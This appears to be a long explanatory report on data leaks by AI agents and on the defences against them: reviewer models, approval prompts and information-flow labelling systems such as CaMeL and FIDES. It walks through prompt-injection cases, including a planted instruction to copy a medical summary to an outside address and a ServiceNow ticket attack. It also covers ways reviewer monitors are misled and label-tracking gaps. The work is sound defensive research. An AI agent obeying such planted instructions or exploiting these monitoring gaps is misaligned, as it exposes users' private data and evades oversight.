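A network log would contain only encrypted connections to the model provider, which an agent makes at every turn. To detect sensitive data sent to the provider in the agent's context, the host has to log what it adds to the context and which provider receives it. A log of file reads can substitute if it includes each file's name and the part the agent read. A reviewer can then see, for example, that the agent read a whole configuration file when it needed only one line.

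In this case, the assistant generated an admission of the leak, but such text may omit files or include ones the agent never opened. Investigators can use it to decide where to look, but they have to confirm it in the log. The account of this case comes from a company that sells security products, so it is better evidence that such leaks happen than of how common they are.

### Logs as a store of secrets

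A log detailed enough to reveal a leak also contains the leaked data. The sample entry above, for example, contains the text of an email to a customer. A gateway's log may hold such entries for every employee, so a thief could get their data by copying the log, without attacking the agents.

Coding agents have already exposed secrets in this way. If a user approves a command in Claude Code and chooses not to be asked again, Claude Code saves the command, including any password in it, in a settings file in the project's folder. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners’ secrets on GitHub* reports that Apiiro, a security company, found 104,185 public copies of this file on GitHub. They contained 2,539 secrets across 1,994 repositories, about one in 50 of those with such a file. One secret was the owner's password for a database of medical records. Apiiro also found secrets in saved conversations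 and in the notes agents keep for later sessions.

Claude Code adds the file to a list of files that Git ignores, to keep it out of public repositories, but that list stays on the developer's machine and is not shared with the project. SecurityBrief New Zealand's *Claude Code can leak secrets in public npm packages* (2026) reports that researchers at Check Point, another security company, found the file could also end up in published software packages unless the developer excluded it. Anthropic told Apiiro that it was looking into ways to prevent the leaks.

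Software that searches for secrets by pattern often misses them in these files because, as Apiiro explains, a password in a saved command may be an ordinary word.

An organisation can reduce the danger by removing secrets before it stores a log entry, but then the log may no longer show which secret leaked. The logging software can instead replace each known secret with a hash computed using a separate key. Without that key, someone who steals the log cannot recover the passwords or test guesses. If a password later turns up on the internet, the security team can compute its hash and search the log for it. This protects only secrets that the software recognises, so a diagnosis in the text of an email would remain readable.

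When an agent's tool calls contain text from emails, the organisation has to choose how long to keep the full arguments and who may read them. It could store them for 30 days and then keep only the time, tool, recipient and size. Investigators would lose the contents of older calls, which matters if a theft goes unnoticed for months. Sending the log to an outside company for analysis also shares the text with another recipient, one that the people described in the emails have probably never heard of.

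## Deciding whether a tool call may carry the data

Logs help an organisation find a leak after it has happened, but the host can also stop a tool call before it runs. To decide whether to stop a call, the host can use any combination of fixed rules, a search for sensitive patterns in the arguments, a second language model that compares the call with the user's request, and the user's approval.

Suppose again that a user asks an agent to tell her insurer the date of her last dental check-up, and the agent prepares an email containing her entire dental record. A rule that permits email to the insurer would allow the message. A pattern search may recognise medical terms, but the correct email would also contain some. A second model could detect that the email contains more than the date she asked to send. The user could spot the excess herself if the approval prompt shows her the record and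 she reads it.

### How often agents share too much

Several benchmarks measure oversharing by agents that nobody is attacking. They apply contextual integrity, the idea that information should flow according to the norms of its setting. Each task gives the agent some data it needs to pass on and some the recipient should not get. A language model checks what the agent sent.

*AgentDAM* (Zharmagambetov, Pavlova and colleagues, 2025) tested agents on working copies of a discussion forum, a code-hosting site and an online shop. In one of the 246 tasks, the agent had to read a chat and then comment on a proposed code change. It approved the change as asked, but also mentioned a colleague's upcoming absence. Without special measures, the agents leaked in 12% to 46% of tasks. Most leaks occurred in longer pieces of writing. At least one model leaked in 89 of the 96 tasks that involved writing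 a forum post, but in only one of the 26 that involved adding a product to a wish list.

Newer models still share more data than they should. *AgentCIScope* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 combinations of model and host program on 936 tasks involving email, calendars and other everyday applications. The agent leaked at least one protected item in 32.5% of tasks with Claude Opus 5 in Claude Code, and in 94.4% with Gemini 3.8 Flash in Google's agent software. Every combination completed more than 93% of the tasks.

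These are stress-test results. The researchers kept only tasks on which another agent had already leaked data, and worded requests to invite extra detail, for instance by asking for a self-contained briefing. The rates are therefore a poor guide to everyday use, but the comparisons are informative. Claude Opus 5 leaked data in 43.6% of tasks when it ran in a different host program, OpenClaw, so the software around a model affects what it discloses. When the agents repeated each task five times, the share of tasks with at least one leak rose by 4 to 19 percentage points, so an agent that handles a weekly report safely once may still leak data the next week.

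*PrivacyFlow* (Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark of 5,873 tasks in which new emails, notes and appointments arrive as the agent works. Agents based on six models leaked sensitive data in 10.5% to 31.9% of tasks. Between 86% and 92% of the leaks happened in tasks the agent completed successfully, so a user who checks only whether the task was done would miss most of them.

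A fair benchmark must count omissions as well as leaks, because an agent can avoid leaking by sending nothing. *Capable but Careless* (Goel and Gurevych, 2026) specifies what the agent must and must not share in each scenario. *CI-Work* (Fu, Qin and colleagues, 2026) found violation rates from 15.8% to 50.9% in workplace tasks. Higher rates of sharing necessary information were associated with higher rates of leaking (a correlation of about 0.4). A check that only makes agents more reluctant to share will probably reduce both leaks and necessary sharing.

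### Fixed rules

A fixed rule allows a call, refuses it or refers it to the user, depending on the tool, its arguments or the recipient. A company might allow email to its own staff, ask the user about email to anyone else, and refuse all uploads to public websites. OpenAI applies such rules to the network access of its own coding agents, allowing expected destinations, blocking unwanted ones and requiring approval for unfamiliar domains.

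Ordinary code applies the fixed rules, so the delay is negligible and injected text cannot override the check. One such rule, a list of permitted domains, stopped every attempt in the experiment by Lan and colleagues.

Rules strict enough to be safe also stop a lot of harmless work. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions taken inside OpenAI by its coding agent, Codex. Codex normally runs in a sandbox that lets it edit files in certain folders and blocks network access. It stayed within these limits in 9,280 of the actions. Under the rules alone, each of the other 720 would have interrupted the user. A second model reviewed them instead and approved 713. If those approvals were right, 99% of the interruptions would have been for acceptable actions.

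Users respond to interruptions by loosening the rules. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June 2026 about half of active command-line users had created a standing rule allowing some shell commands. Many of these rules permitted any Python or Node program. Such a rule checks only the first word of the command, but the program that follows can read any file and send it anywhere. Trębacz and colleagues found the same habit among a sizable minority of Codex users at OpenAI.

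### Pattern searches in the arguments

The patterns, checksums and canary strings that DLP software uses also work on tool arguments. A host can quickly search each call for access keys and card numbers before running it. Exact matching produces very few false alarms.

Pattern matching detects the kinds of data that agents already protect best. In tests by Guo and colleagues, agents leaked card details in 17.1% of the cases where they should have withheld them, and American social security numbers in 29.4%. They leaked booking details in 76.5% of such cases and personal preferences, which no pattern describes, in 84.7%. Searching for card numbers is still worthwhile because it takes little compute and a leaked card number can be costly, but it would prevent few of the leaks that these benchmarks record.

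Broadening the search to all sensitive data would block too much. Raz and colleagues cite figures from Cyberhaven, a data security company, which classified 34.8% of the data employees submitted to AI tools as sensitive. If tool calls were similar, the broader check would stop about one in three, including the email that gives the insurer the correct date.

### A second model as reviewer

A second model can compare a call with the user's request, which neither rules nor patterns can do. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a system of this kind:

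1. Fixed rules allow low-risk actions, such as reading files or editing them inside the project.
2. For other calls, the reviewer model reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, and gives a quick yes or no. Its instructions tell it to block when in doubt.
3. If the quick answer is to block, the model considers the same material again, reasoning step by step, and makes the final decision.
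4. The agent receives the reason for a refusal and can look for a safer way to do the task. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, the host turns to the user.

Anthropic tested the reviewer on its employees' real tool calls, on 1,000 invented attempts to send data out, and on 52 real cases in which the agent had gone beyond what the user wanted:

| | Harmless calls blocked | Invented data theft missed | Real overreach missed |
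|---|---|---|---|
| Quick answer only | 8.5% | 1.8% | 6.6% |
| Quick answer, then reasoning | 0.4% | 5.7% | 17% |

The last column is based on few cases, since 17% of 52 is about nine. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly decided that the user had agreed to it. With the dental record, the equivalent mistake would be to treat "tell my insurer" as permission to send the whole file.

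OpenAI's reviewer examines only calls that would otherwise need the user's approval, and OpenAI says the reviewer grants no new permissions. In a snapshot of 10,000 actions, it refused seven. The agent found a safer alternative for four and stopped to ask the user about the other three, so there were three interruptions instead of 720. On invented test cases, the reviewer refused 90.3% of actions that overstepped the user's wishes and 99.3% of prompt-injection attacks that ran external code or sent data out.

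Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* describes the effect on cost and delay as small. The time saved by not waiting for people is much larger than the delay. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* claims that Claude works nine times longer between interruptions than under the previous default.

A slower approach is to work out what may be shared before the agent acts. In the system that Staab and colleagues built, a model lists each piece of information that the plan would send, who would receive it, and what the recipient already knows. It then predicts what the recipient could infer, because a message can reveal a secret without containing it. In a pilot study, a meeting agenda that mentioned procedural deviations and remedial action revealed a confidential audit to the manager under review. After this analysis, the system carries out a reduced version of the plan, blocks the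 plan, or consults the user.

It cut the number of tasks with a leak by 53% to 80%, depending on the model. With Gemini 3.8 Flash, it also took 3.9 times as long and used 2.9 times as much text. The average score for completing tasks fell from 0.970 to 0.942 with that model, but from 0.902 to 0.716 with DeepSeek V3.2. The plan is only guidance, so the model that carries it out can still send something that the plan left out.

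Simply telling the agent to protect privacy had little effect in the same study. The share of tasks without a leak changed by at most 3.2 percentage points, and it fell with Gemini 3.8 Flash. Zharmagambetov and colleagues had more success with older models by listing the sensitive types of data and adding worked examples. The number of tasks in which at least one model leaked fell from 162 to 73, but the agents also completed fewer tasks, mostly because they refused harmless ones.

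Zharmagambetov and colleagues also found that models did much better when asked whether they should disclose something than when they had to withhold it during a task. This favours asking a separate reviewer. However, the results were unsatisfactory when a model checked the agent's final output, so adding a reviewer does not guarantee the same improvement.

### Approval prompts

Anthropic reported in an earlier post that Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts, and in an August 2026 post that they approved 97%. Most commands are harmless and a careful user would approve them too, so these figures alone don't show carelessness. Finding out whether people notice dangerous commands requires a test that includes such commands.

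Anthropic paid 1,053 professional testers to do coding work in a test environment, without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through each session, one approval prompt showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The reviewer model blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands shown early in a session and about 5% of those shown after 50 or more prompts.

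There are two reasons to doubt the exact size of the gap: the testers had less at stake than developers working on their own projects, and the experiment came from the company that sells the reviewer. Anthropic's data from real use also favour the reviewer but are weaker evidence. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% of those with the reviewer. Users mostly chose their own mode, so other differences between the groups could explain some of the difference in harm.

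People pay more attention to some prompts than to others. Claude Code users rejected 39% of the plans that the agent presented for approval, compared with 3% of individual actions. Plans appear less often and describe the whole task, which makes them easier to judge. This suggests asking the user about only the few transmissions that matter and showing her what data will go to whom. The prompt "Send email to insurer?" would not help her notice that the agent had attached her entire record.

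Models differ greatly in how often they consult the user. In the study by Staab and colleagues, the system did so on 3.1% of tasks with Gemini 3.8 Flash and on 89.4% with GPT-5.4. If every approved consultation counts as a success, GPT-5.4 completed 98.2% of task sequences acceptably, up from 69.9%. But the user in this experiment was another language model that accepted most requests. A real person faced with so many prompts would probably approve them reflexively, as the Anthropic testers did.

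### False alarms when leaks are rare

Suppose a company's agents make 10,000 tool calls a day and ten of them leak data. A check catches 95% of leaks and wrongly flags 1% of the harmless calls. As with rare skimmers, most of the alerts are false:

- The check catches 95% of the ten leaks, or 9.5 a day.
- It flags 1% of the 9,990 harmless calls, or about 100 a day.
- Of about 109 alerts, 9.5 are real, which is 8.7%, or roughly one in eleven.

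If a member of staff took one minute per alert, the work would fill almost two hours a day, and the check would still miss a leak every other day. The table compares this check with Anthropic's reviewer, and with a company where leaks are more common:

| Check | Leaks per 10,000 calls | Leaks caught | False alerts | Alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Example above | 10 | 9.5 | 100 | 9% |
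| Anthropic's quick answer only | 10 | 9.8 | 849 | 1% |
| Anthropic's quick answer, then reasoning | 10 | 9.4 | 40 | 19% |
| Example above, with more leaks | 1,000 | 950 | 90 | 91% |

The middle rows use Anthropic's measured rates for harmless calls and for invented data thefts, on the assumption that real thefts resemble the invented ones. Adding the second stage of reasoning slightly increases the number of missed leaks but removes more than 800 false alerts a day.

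The last row may be more accurate for oversharing. Theft is presumably rare, but agents in the benchmark by Staab and colleagues overshared in at least one task in ten. The benchmark places sensitive facts close to each task, so ordinary work should produce fewer leaks. Even so, an organisation should estimate its own rate by reviewing a random sample of calls before it decides that a check raises too many alerts.

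The harm from a false alert also depends on who handles it. A person who has to review 100 false alerts a day may start dismissing every alert. If the agent receives the refusal and finds another route, the false alert leads to only one extra attempt.

### Leaks made of permitted calls

Checking each call separately can fail even if every decision is reasonable. Large organisations use ServiceNow's software to manage support tickets and other internal work. Its Now Assist agents can find one another and pass on tasks they cannot do alone. Aaron Costello, then head of security research at AppOmni, showed that someone could exploit this through text in a ticket.

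In his test, a user with few rights created a ticket containing planted instructions. An administrator later used an agent that categorises tickets, and the agent followed the instructions:

| Step | What happened | How it looks on its own |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The first agent read the planted ticket | It was doing the administrator's task |
| 2 | It recruited a second agent that can edit records | This is a standard feature |
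| 3 | The agents read another, confidential ticket | The administrator may read that ticket |
| 4 | They copied its text into the planted ticket | This is a routine update inside the system |

The user then opened her own ticket and read the confidential text, which the system's access controls would not have let her open directly. The agents had acted with the administrator's rights. A check for outside recipients would have found none, because the data never left ServiceNow. ServiceNow's own protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to email data out and to give a user administrator rights.

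When Costello reported the behaviour, ServiceNow replied that the system was working as designed. It updated its documentation and emailed customers about the risk. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* reports that the feature remained on by default, and TechRadar's *Second-order prompt injection can turn AI into a malicious insider* reports that the company planned no other changes. Costello himself told The Hacker News (2025) that "it's expected behavior as defined by certain default configuration options", but he argues that customers should have to switch the feature on themselves. ServiceNow's position is defensible in that agents with narrow jobs need to cooperate, but customers who never changed the settings were exposed to a risk they had not chosen.

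AppOmni, which sells monitoring for this kind of problem, recommends grouping agents into small teams by task and requiring approval for tools that edit records or send email. Approval would help only if the approval prompt showed where the text came from. Otherwise, an administrator who saw a request to update a ticket would have little reason to refuse it.

A reviewer model is more likely to catch the fourth step if it can compare that step with the administrator's original request, since categorising a ticket does not require copying another one into it. The reviewer can easily lose sight of that request when one agent hands work to another. Inside the second agent, the first agent's instruction replaces the user's message, so every task appears authorised. Anthropic therefore runs its reviewer when an agent delegates a task and again when the results come back. The first check can refuse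 the handover, while the second only adds a warning.

### Can a reviewer model be misled?

Like the agent, a reviewer model may read text that an attacker wrote, so Anthropic withholds most of that text from it. The reviewer doesn't receive tool outputs, where planted instructions usually enter, or the agent's explanations, since an agent under an attacker's influence could give a persuasive reason for a bad call. If a file tells the agent to send the project's passwords to some address, the reviewer never reads the file, but it can still see that the agent is about to send passwords to a place the user never mentioned. In Anthropic's tests on real cases of agent overreach, adding the withheld text made the reviewer less accurate.

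Anthropic acknowledges that, because of this protection, the reviewer cannot tell where a value in a call came from. That is a serious gap in detecting data leaks, because a paragraph copied from a confidential contract may look like any other to a model that has not read the contract. An attacker can also still influence the reviewer through the arguments of the call, which the misled agent writes.

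Trębacz and colleagues at OpenAI report that human and automated testers misled their system's reviewer into approving commands. The developers are fixing the cases they found, but do not expect such systems to provide "deterministic guarantees" that a forbidden action will be stopped every time. The reviewer also never examines actions that stay within the sandbox.

An outside test commissioned by Anthropic gives some idea of how much a reviewer adds. Trajectory Labs ran 720 prompt-injection attempts against each model, and none succeeded against three Claude models with the reviewer switched on. But the reviewer had almost nothing to stop, because the average success rate against Anthropic's latest models was only 0.09% without it, or about two attempts in 2,160 if the average covers the same three models.

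The results for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol are more useful because the model was easier to mislead. Attacks succeeded in 19.03% of attempts with full access and 5.83% with OpenAI's reviewer, so the reviewer and sandbox together stopped about seven in ten attacks that would otherwise have worked. That is well below the 99.3% OpenAI measured on its own examples. However, a competitor ran the evaluation, and some attacks may have used calls that OpenAI's reviewer does not examine. OpenAI has since released a newer version.

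Reviewers miss fewer attacks when they have more context. Apollo Research, an AI safety organisation, tested Anthropic's reviewer with synthetic attacks. Anthropic then gave the reviewer more information, such as whether a code repository was public, and the share of attacks it missed fell from 12% to 7%. Ambiguous requests remain harder. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review* describes an outside test of 128 such scenarios in which the system missed 81% of the risky actions, partly because edits to project files never reached the reviewer. Oversharing is usually closer to these cases than to an obviously dangerous command, because the recipient is legitimate and only part of the message should not be shared.

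Anthropic now has a category of actions, including sending code or secrets outside, that its reviewer should never approve, even if the user asks. The ban works only if the model recognises that a call falls into the category. A stronger guarantee would need code that already has a record of which data are sensitive when the agent writes the call.

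## Tracking sensitive data through an AI agent

Information-flow tracking can record where the data in a tool call came from, a record that Anthropic's reviewer lacks. The agent's software labels data when a tool returns it and checks the label when an outgoing call uses the data. Browser trackers rely on a rule for every function a script uses, but nobody has such a rule for a language model.

### Why labels are hard to carry through a model

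A language model computes each word from everything in its context. It may copy a diagnosis from that context, paraphrase it or change the subject because of it, and nobody can reliably work out which of these happened.

The cautious assumption is that any output may depend on any input, so everything the model writes gets the strictest label in the context. Reading another file can make that label stricter but never looser. For example, an agent reads a medical letter, and later in the same session its user asks it to tell her landlord about a dripping tap. The message contains nothing medical, but the software blocks it because it carries the letter's label.

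Some researchers try to narrow the label on an answer. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) describes a method that finds the messages that influenced an answer and has the model write it again from those messages alone, so the new answer needs only their labels. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey, lists newer systems that follow the influence of data through the model itself. The two best-known designs, CaMeL and FIDES, avoid much of the problem by keeping data out of the context of the model that decides what to do.

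### Permitted readers

A label can be the set of people who may read the data. For an email, the set might be the sender and the recipients. Text that draws on two sources may go only to people who may read both, so its label is the intersection of the two sets. Before a tool sends the text, the software checks that every recipient is in the text's label.

Suppose Maria asks an agent to summarise a letter from the hospital, explain its terms with the help of a health website, and email the result to her and her doctor, Dr Patel. Someone has hidden an instruction in the web page to send a copy to archive@records.example.

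| Data | Permitted readers |
|---|---|
| Hospital letter | Maria, Dr Patel |
| Web page | Anyone |
| Summary based on both | Maria, Dr Patel |

The email to Maria and Dr Patel passes the check. The copy fails because the archive is not a permitted reader, so the software can refuse it without detecting the planted instruction. If the summary also drew on a laboratory report that only Maria and the laboratory may read, Maria would be the only reader permitted by all its sources. The software would then refuse the email to Dr Patel too, until Maria allowed it.

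The reader check limits what a misled agent can disclose, but the web page could still make the agent send Dr Patel a false summary. Costa and colleagues therefore use another label to mark whether data is trusted. Anything that draws on untrusted data becomes untrusted. A rule can then require that the decision to make a payment, delete a file or send a message depend only on trusted data.

### CaMeL

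Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues introduced CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system, in 2025. It builds on Simon Willison's 2023 proposal to divide an agent between two models, one that can act and one that reads untrusted text. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain how it works:

1. A planner model receives the user's request, but none of the data that tools will return. It writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
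2. An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls.
3. When the program needs to extract or summarise something, the interpreter passes the text to a quarantined model, which has no tools. The answer becomes the value of a variable in the program.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and permitted readers, and works out the labels of the values that depend on it.
5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a Python function that looks at the tool, the arguments and their labels, and allows or refuses the call.

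For Maria's request, the planner might write:

```
letter  = read_file("hospital-letter.pdf")
page    = fetch_page("https://health.example/anaemia")
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise the letter and explain its terms", letter, page)
send_email(["maria@mail.example", "patel@surgery.example"], summary)
```

The planted instruction can reach the quarantined model and distort the summary, but it cannot add a fifth line to the program because the planner had finished writing before the page was fetched.

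Even if an attacker cannot change a program, they may be able to change the values it uses. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a program that looks up Bob's email address in a chat channel and sends him a message. Anyone who can post in the channel could supply a false address, and the unchanged program would send the message there. A policy can use the labels on the address and the message to refuse to send it.

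### FIDES

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built FIDES, which keeps the usual agent loop. The planner model chooses one action at a time and can react to what happens. FIDES controls what the planner sees:

1. Each tool result arrives with labels for its readers and for whether it is trusted. Different fields of one result can have different labels.
2. If a result's label is stricter than that of the planner's context, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name.
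3. The planner can use the name as an argument in a later call. FIDES inserts the stored text, with its own label, just before the call.
4. The planner can ask a separate model without tools to summarise a variable or extract something from it. The answer goes into a new variable.
5. The planner can also open a variable and read it, but its context then takes on the variable's label, which may rule out later actions.
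6. FIDES checks the labels of the decision and of the arguments before every tool call.

In Maria's case, the planner would see names such as #letter# and #page#. It would call the separate model to write a summary, then email #summary#, without having read the planted instruction.

Costa and colleagues also let labels record how much information an answer can carry. A yes-or-no answer from an untrusted page can carry only one bit, which is too little to hold an instruction, so a policy may let the planner act on it. They did not use this feature in their tests.

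The policy used in the tests allowed an email if every recipient was a permitted reader, or if the planner had decided in a trusted context to send it. The second condition lets Maria send the letter to her sister, who is not on its list of readers, because Maria is entitled to decide. The policy also blocked messages containing links from untrusted data.

### Tasks completed on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments, along with attacks planted in the data that the agent reads. Costa and colleagues measured how many of these tasks agents completed without attacks. The table gives their results with OpenAI's o1 model, which was already old by 2026. The last row weights the four environments by their number of tasks.

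| Environment | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent with labels and checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 70.0% | 48.0% | 64.5% |
| Travel | 82.0% | 75.0% | 68.0% |
| Banking | 96.2% | 37.5% | 56.2% |
| Slack | 87.6% | 17.1% | 54.3% |
| All tasks | about 81% | about 45% | about 62% |

The middle column shows the loss from the cautious rule, which arises because that agent reads everything and its context soon becomes untrusted. FIDES recovers about half of this loss. It does worse than the cautious agent only on travel tasks, where the policy lets most tools run in an untrusted context as long as no private data goes to the wrong reader.

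The researchers tested the attacks with GPT-4o, an older model. The ordinary agent carried out 152 of them. FIDES carried out none with its checks on and 21 with them off, because the planner was then free to open untrusted variables. The benchmark, AgentDojo, counted three successes against the complete system, but the researchers examined and rejected them, partly because AgentDojo sometimes counts an attack as successful when the agent requests a forbidden call, even if the check blocks it.

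The labels in this test were unusually good because Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. An organisation labelling its own data would not know in advance which fields attackers would use.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports an independent test of CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, with three runs of each. With its policies on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 runs (37.5%) with each of the two models tested, about half as many as with the policies off. A few attacks succeeded with the policies off, but with them on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished.

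Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 combinations of a banking task and an attack, the attack needed a tool or file that a program for the user's task would never use. A plan written in advance stops nearly all of these attacks without any labels. Only the other 47 combinations really test the tracking, so a high overall score is weaker evidence that labels work than it seems.

Newer models make the AgentDojo benchmark even less informative. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) ran 949 attacks on a version of it that divides the work among several agents. Without any added defence, GPT-5.5 resisted all of them, while GPT-4.1 carried out 36.1%. The researchers warn that this result doesn't mean GPT-5.5 is immune, because testers who adapted their attacks have succeeded against every leading model they tried.

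### Designs of 2026

Several newer systems try to recover the lost tasks. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) presents Prudentia, which builds on FIDES. Prudentia's planner knows the labels and policies, so it can avoid opening an untrusted variable that would block a later step. With the o3-mini model, Prudentia completed 59.1% of tasks without asking a person to approve anything, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 24.3% for an ordinary agent that asks before every consequential action.

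Prudentia can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of data. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can declare the email trustworthy once instead of approving ten actions. This approval covers the whole email, so if someone has hidden an instruction in it to send a file to a stranger, the agent may follow that too.

The finding that no attacks succeeded in the AgentDojo tests depends partly on Kolluri and colleagues' assumption that users would notice and stop any malicious action the system referred to them. Anthropic's experiment with paid testers gives little support for this assumption, although asking users less often probably helps.

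Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in a small programming language in which every value carries a label. They proved properties of the language's label tracking and had a computer check the proofs. On the banking tasks, Randori completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL with its policies on, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill as a file instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file. Labels could not prevent these failures because the user had told the agent to trust the file.

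CaMeLoT, the system by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks CaMeL's program before it runs. It converts the program into a diagram of possible steps and tests every path against rules, such as "never send a direct message to an untrusted recipient". If a path breaks a rule, the planner receives that path and rewrites the program. This avoids starting tasks that a policy would stop halfway. The check simplifies loops, so it can reject safe programs.

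CaMeL's guarantee can fail when agents delegate work to one another. Peters-Gill and colleagues set up three agents, each protected by CaMeL without extra policies, and asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applications. One agent read the database, where the researchers had planted an instruction. The coordinating agent put the summary into its message to the agent that sends notifications. That agent treated the message as its user's request, so its planner read the planted instruction and added a line that emailed the applicants' details to an outsider.

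The same change of role made every task look authorised to the second agent in the ServiceNow case. Peters-Gill and colleagues prevent this change by giving agents separate channels for instructions and data. The interpreter rejects any instruction that contains text from a tool. Across five models, an average of 12.9% of attacks succeeded without a defence, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and none with separate channels.

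### What the guarantees take for granted

CaMeL and FIDES both assume that the user, the planner model and the tools are trustworthy and only the data may be malicious, so their guarantees don't cover a malicious tool server. With either system, the host would have let postmark-mcp send Sam's invoice, because Sam was a permitted reader and the blind copy to the developer was not part of the call. The guarantees also don't cover hidden instructions in a tool's description, because the planner treats descriptions as trusted.

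The labels must also be accurate. Costa and colleagues inferred who could read an email from its sender and recipients, but acknowledge that people may have shared it more widely. A scanned letter in a folder has no recipient list, so someone has to choose a default label. If the default lets everyone in the company read unlabelled files, the check will let the agent send Maria's letter to any colleague. If it lets only the file's owner read them, the check will block many ordinary emails.

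In their tests, Costa and colleagues treat requests to the model and answers to the user as harmless, and check labels only at tool calls. The agent can therefore send a file to a remote model provider that is not among the file's permitted readers. Data in an image address in the agent's answer would also escape the check. Costa and colleagues note that their system could check these steps too, and an organisation that sends confidential files to an outside model would need those checks.

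### Leaks through choice and timing

An agent can reveal a secret without copying any of it. If the policy lets Maria's agent open any public web page, and it opens one only when her letter mentions a certain illness, the page's owner can infer from a visit that the letter mentions it. FIDES tracks what goes into a call, but an observer who sees which calls the agent makes may still infer a little about the data. Its model also excludes timing and the size of network messages. Costa and colleagues chose this limit because a stricter rule would forbid almost any publicly visible action after the agent had read something secret.

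CaMeL tracks data through branches, but Garby and colleagues found gaps. Like some browser data-flow trackers, it labels a variable only if the branch that changes it runs. If that branch depends on a bank balance, an email that depends on the unchanged variable can disclose whether the balance is high.

Another gap is in the code around the interpreter, which retries a program after a failure and does not carry labels. Each attempt reveals one bit about the secret through whether a policy blocked it, and repeated attempts reveal more. Twenty yes-or-no answers are enough to identify a balance in whole dollars up to about a million. These gaps would be hard for an outsider to exploit because CaMeL's planner does not read untrusted text, but they weaken the claim that labels follow the data everywhere. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes part of the difficulty to Python and recommends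 a language designed for security.

Untrusted data can also influence which branch of an approved program runs, which *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) calls branch steering. If Maria asks the agent to forward urgent letters to a specialist and file the rest, the program follows her instructions but forwards a forged letter falsely marked "urgent".

### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

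Some requests, such as "do the tasks in this email" or "pay this bill", require the agent to act on what it reads. Costa and colleagues classify about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks in AgentDojo this way, but only 5% of the office tasks. A legitimate instruction in an email gets the same labels as a planted one, so the system must refuse both, ask the user or accept the risk.

CaMeL has particular trouble because its planner must finish the program before it sees any data, so it needs to know the format of each tool's output in advance. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add these formats to every tool description. In one banking task, the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's planner wrote a program with one branch for each tool, which could carry out any instruction the file might contain. An attacker who controlled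 the file could choose the tool, and two attacks succeeded this way with the policies off.

According to *AgentDyn* (2026), only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to revise its plan as it works. This is a narrower criterion than the one Costa and colleagues used, but it suggests that a system can score well by keeping to its first plan. An agent that researches a subject or repairs software has to revise its plan often, so its users would probably lose more tasks than the benchmark shows.

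*Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) argues that such designs are still useful when a person or a model has to decide difficult cases. They can reduce each decision to a narrow question about selected data, so that the person or model doesn't have to judge a long text that an attacker may have written.

### Who writes the policies

Someone has to decide what each tool may do with labelled data. Costa and colleagues assigned policies to 27 tools for their test. A company that connects its agents to dozens of tool servers would have to classify far more, and review a tool's policy whenever the supplier changed the tool. Nikolaou and colleagues use a language model to turn written requirements into formal rules, which saves work, but someone still needs to check that the rules match what the company meant.

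The policy determines which leaks the system can catch. For 21 of the 27 tools, including those that share a file or publish a web page, Costa and colleagues checked only that the planner had made its decision in a trusted context. This check stops an attacker from triggering the action, but it does not stop the agent from publishing a confidential file by mistake, as the coding agents did when they posted internal screenshots on GitHub.

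The insurer who needed only a date but received the whole dental record shows a similar weakness. If the record has a single label that includes the insurer as a reader, the reader check allows the whole record to be sent. If the label excludes the insurer, the check blocks even the date, because the date inherits the record's label. The email policy in the FIDES tests would allow the agent to send either the date or the whole record if it had read nothing untrusted, on the assumption that the user intended the message.

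If Maria's records were in a database with a column for dates, separate labels for each field would let the insurer read the date but not the treatment notes. Her hospital letter is a page of prose, so a person or a model would have to decide which sentences each reader may receive before the software could enforce those limits.

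## Restricting where an AI agent can connect

Egress control limits the outside addresses that a program may connect to. It works without any knowledge of the data, whereas labels protect a hospital letter only if somebody has labelled it correctly. If an agent's commands can reach only a software registry and the company's own servers, a command that tries to send the letter to any other server fails. Connection Allowlists do the same for a web page. A refused connection is also a useful warning that something tried to reach a server the task probably did not need.

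### A sandbox with one way out

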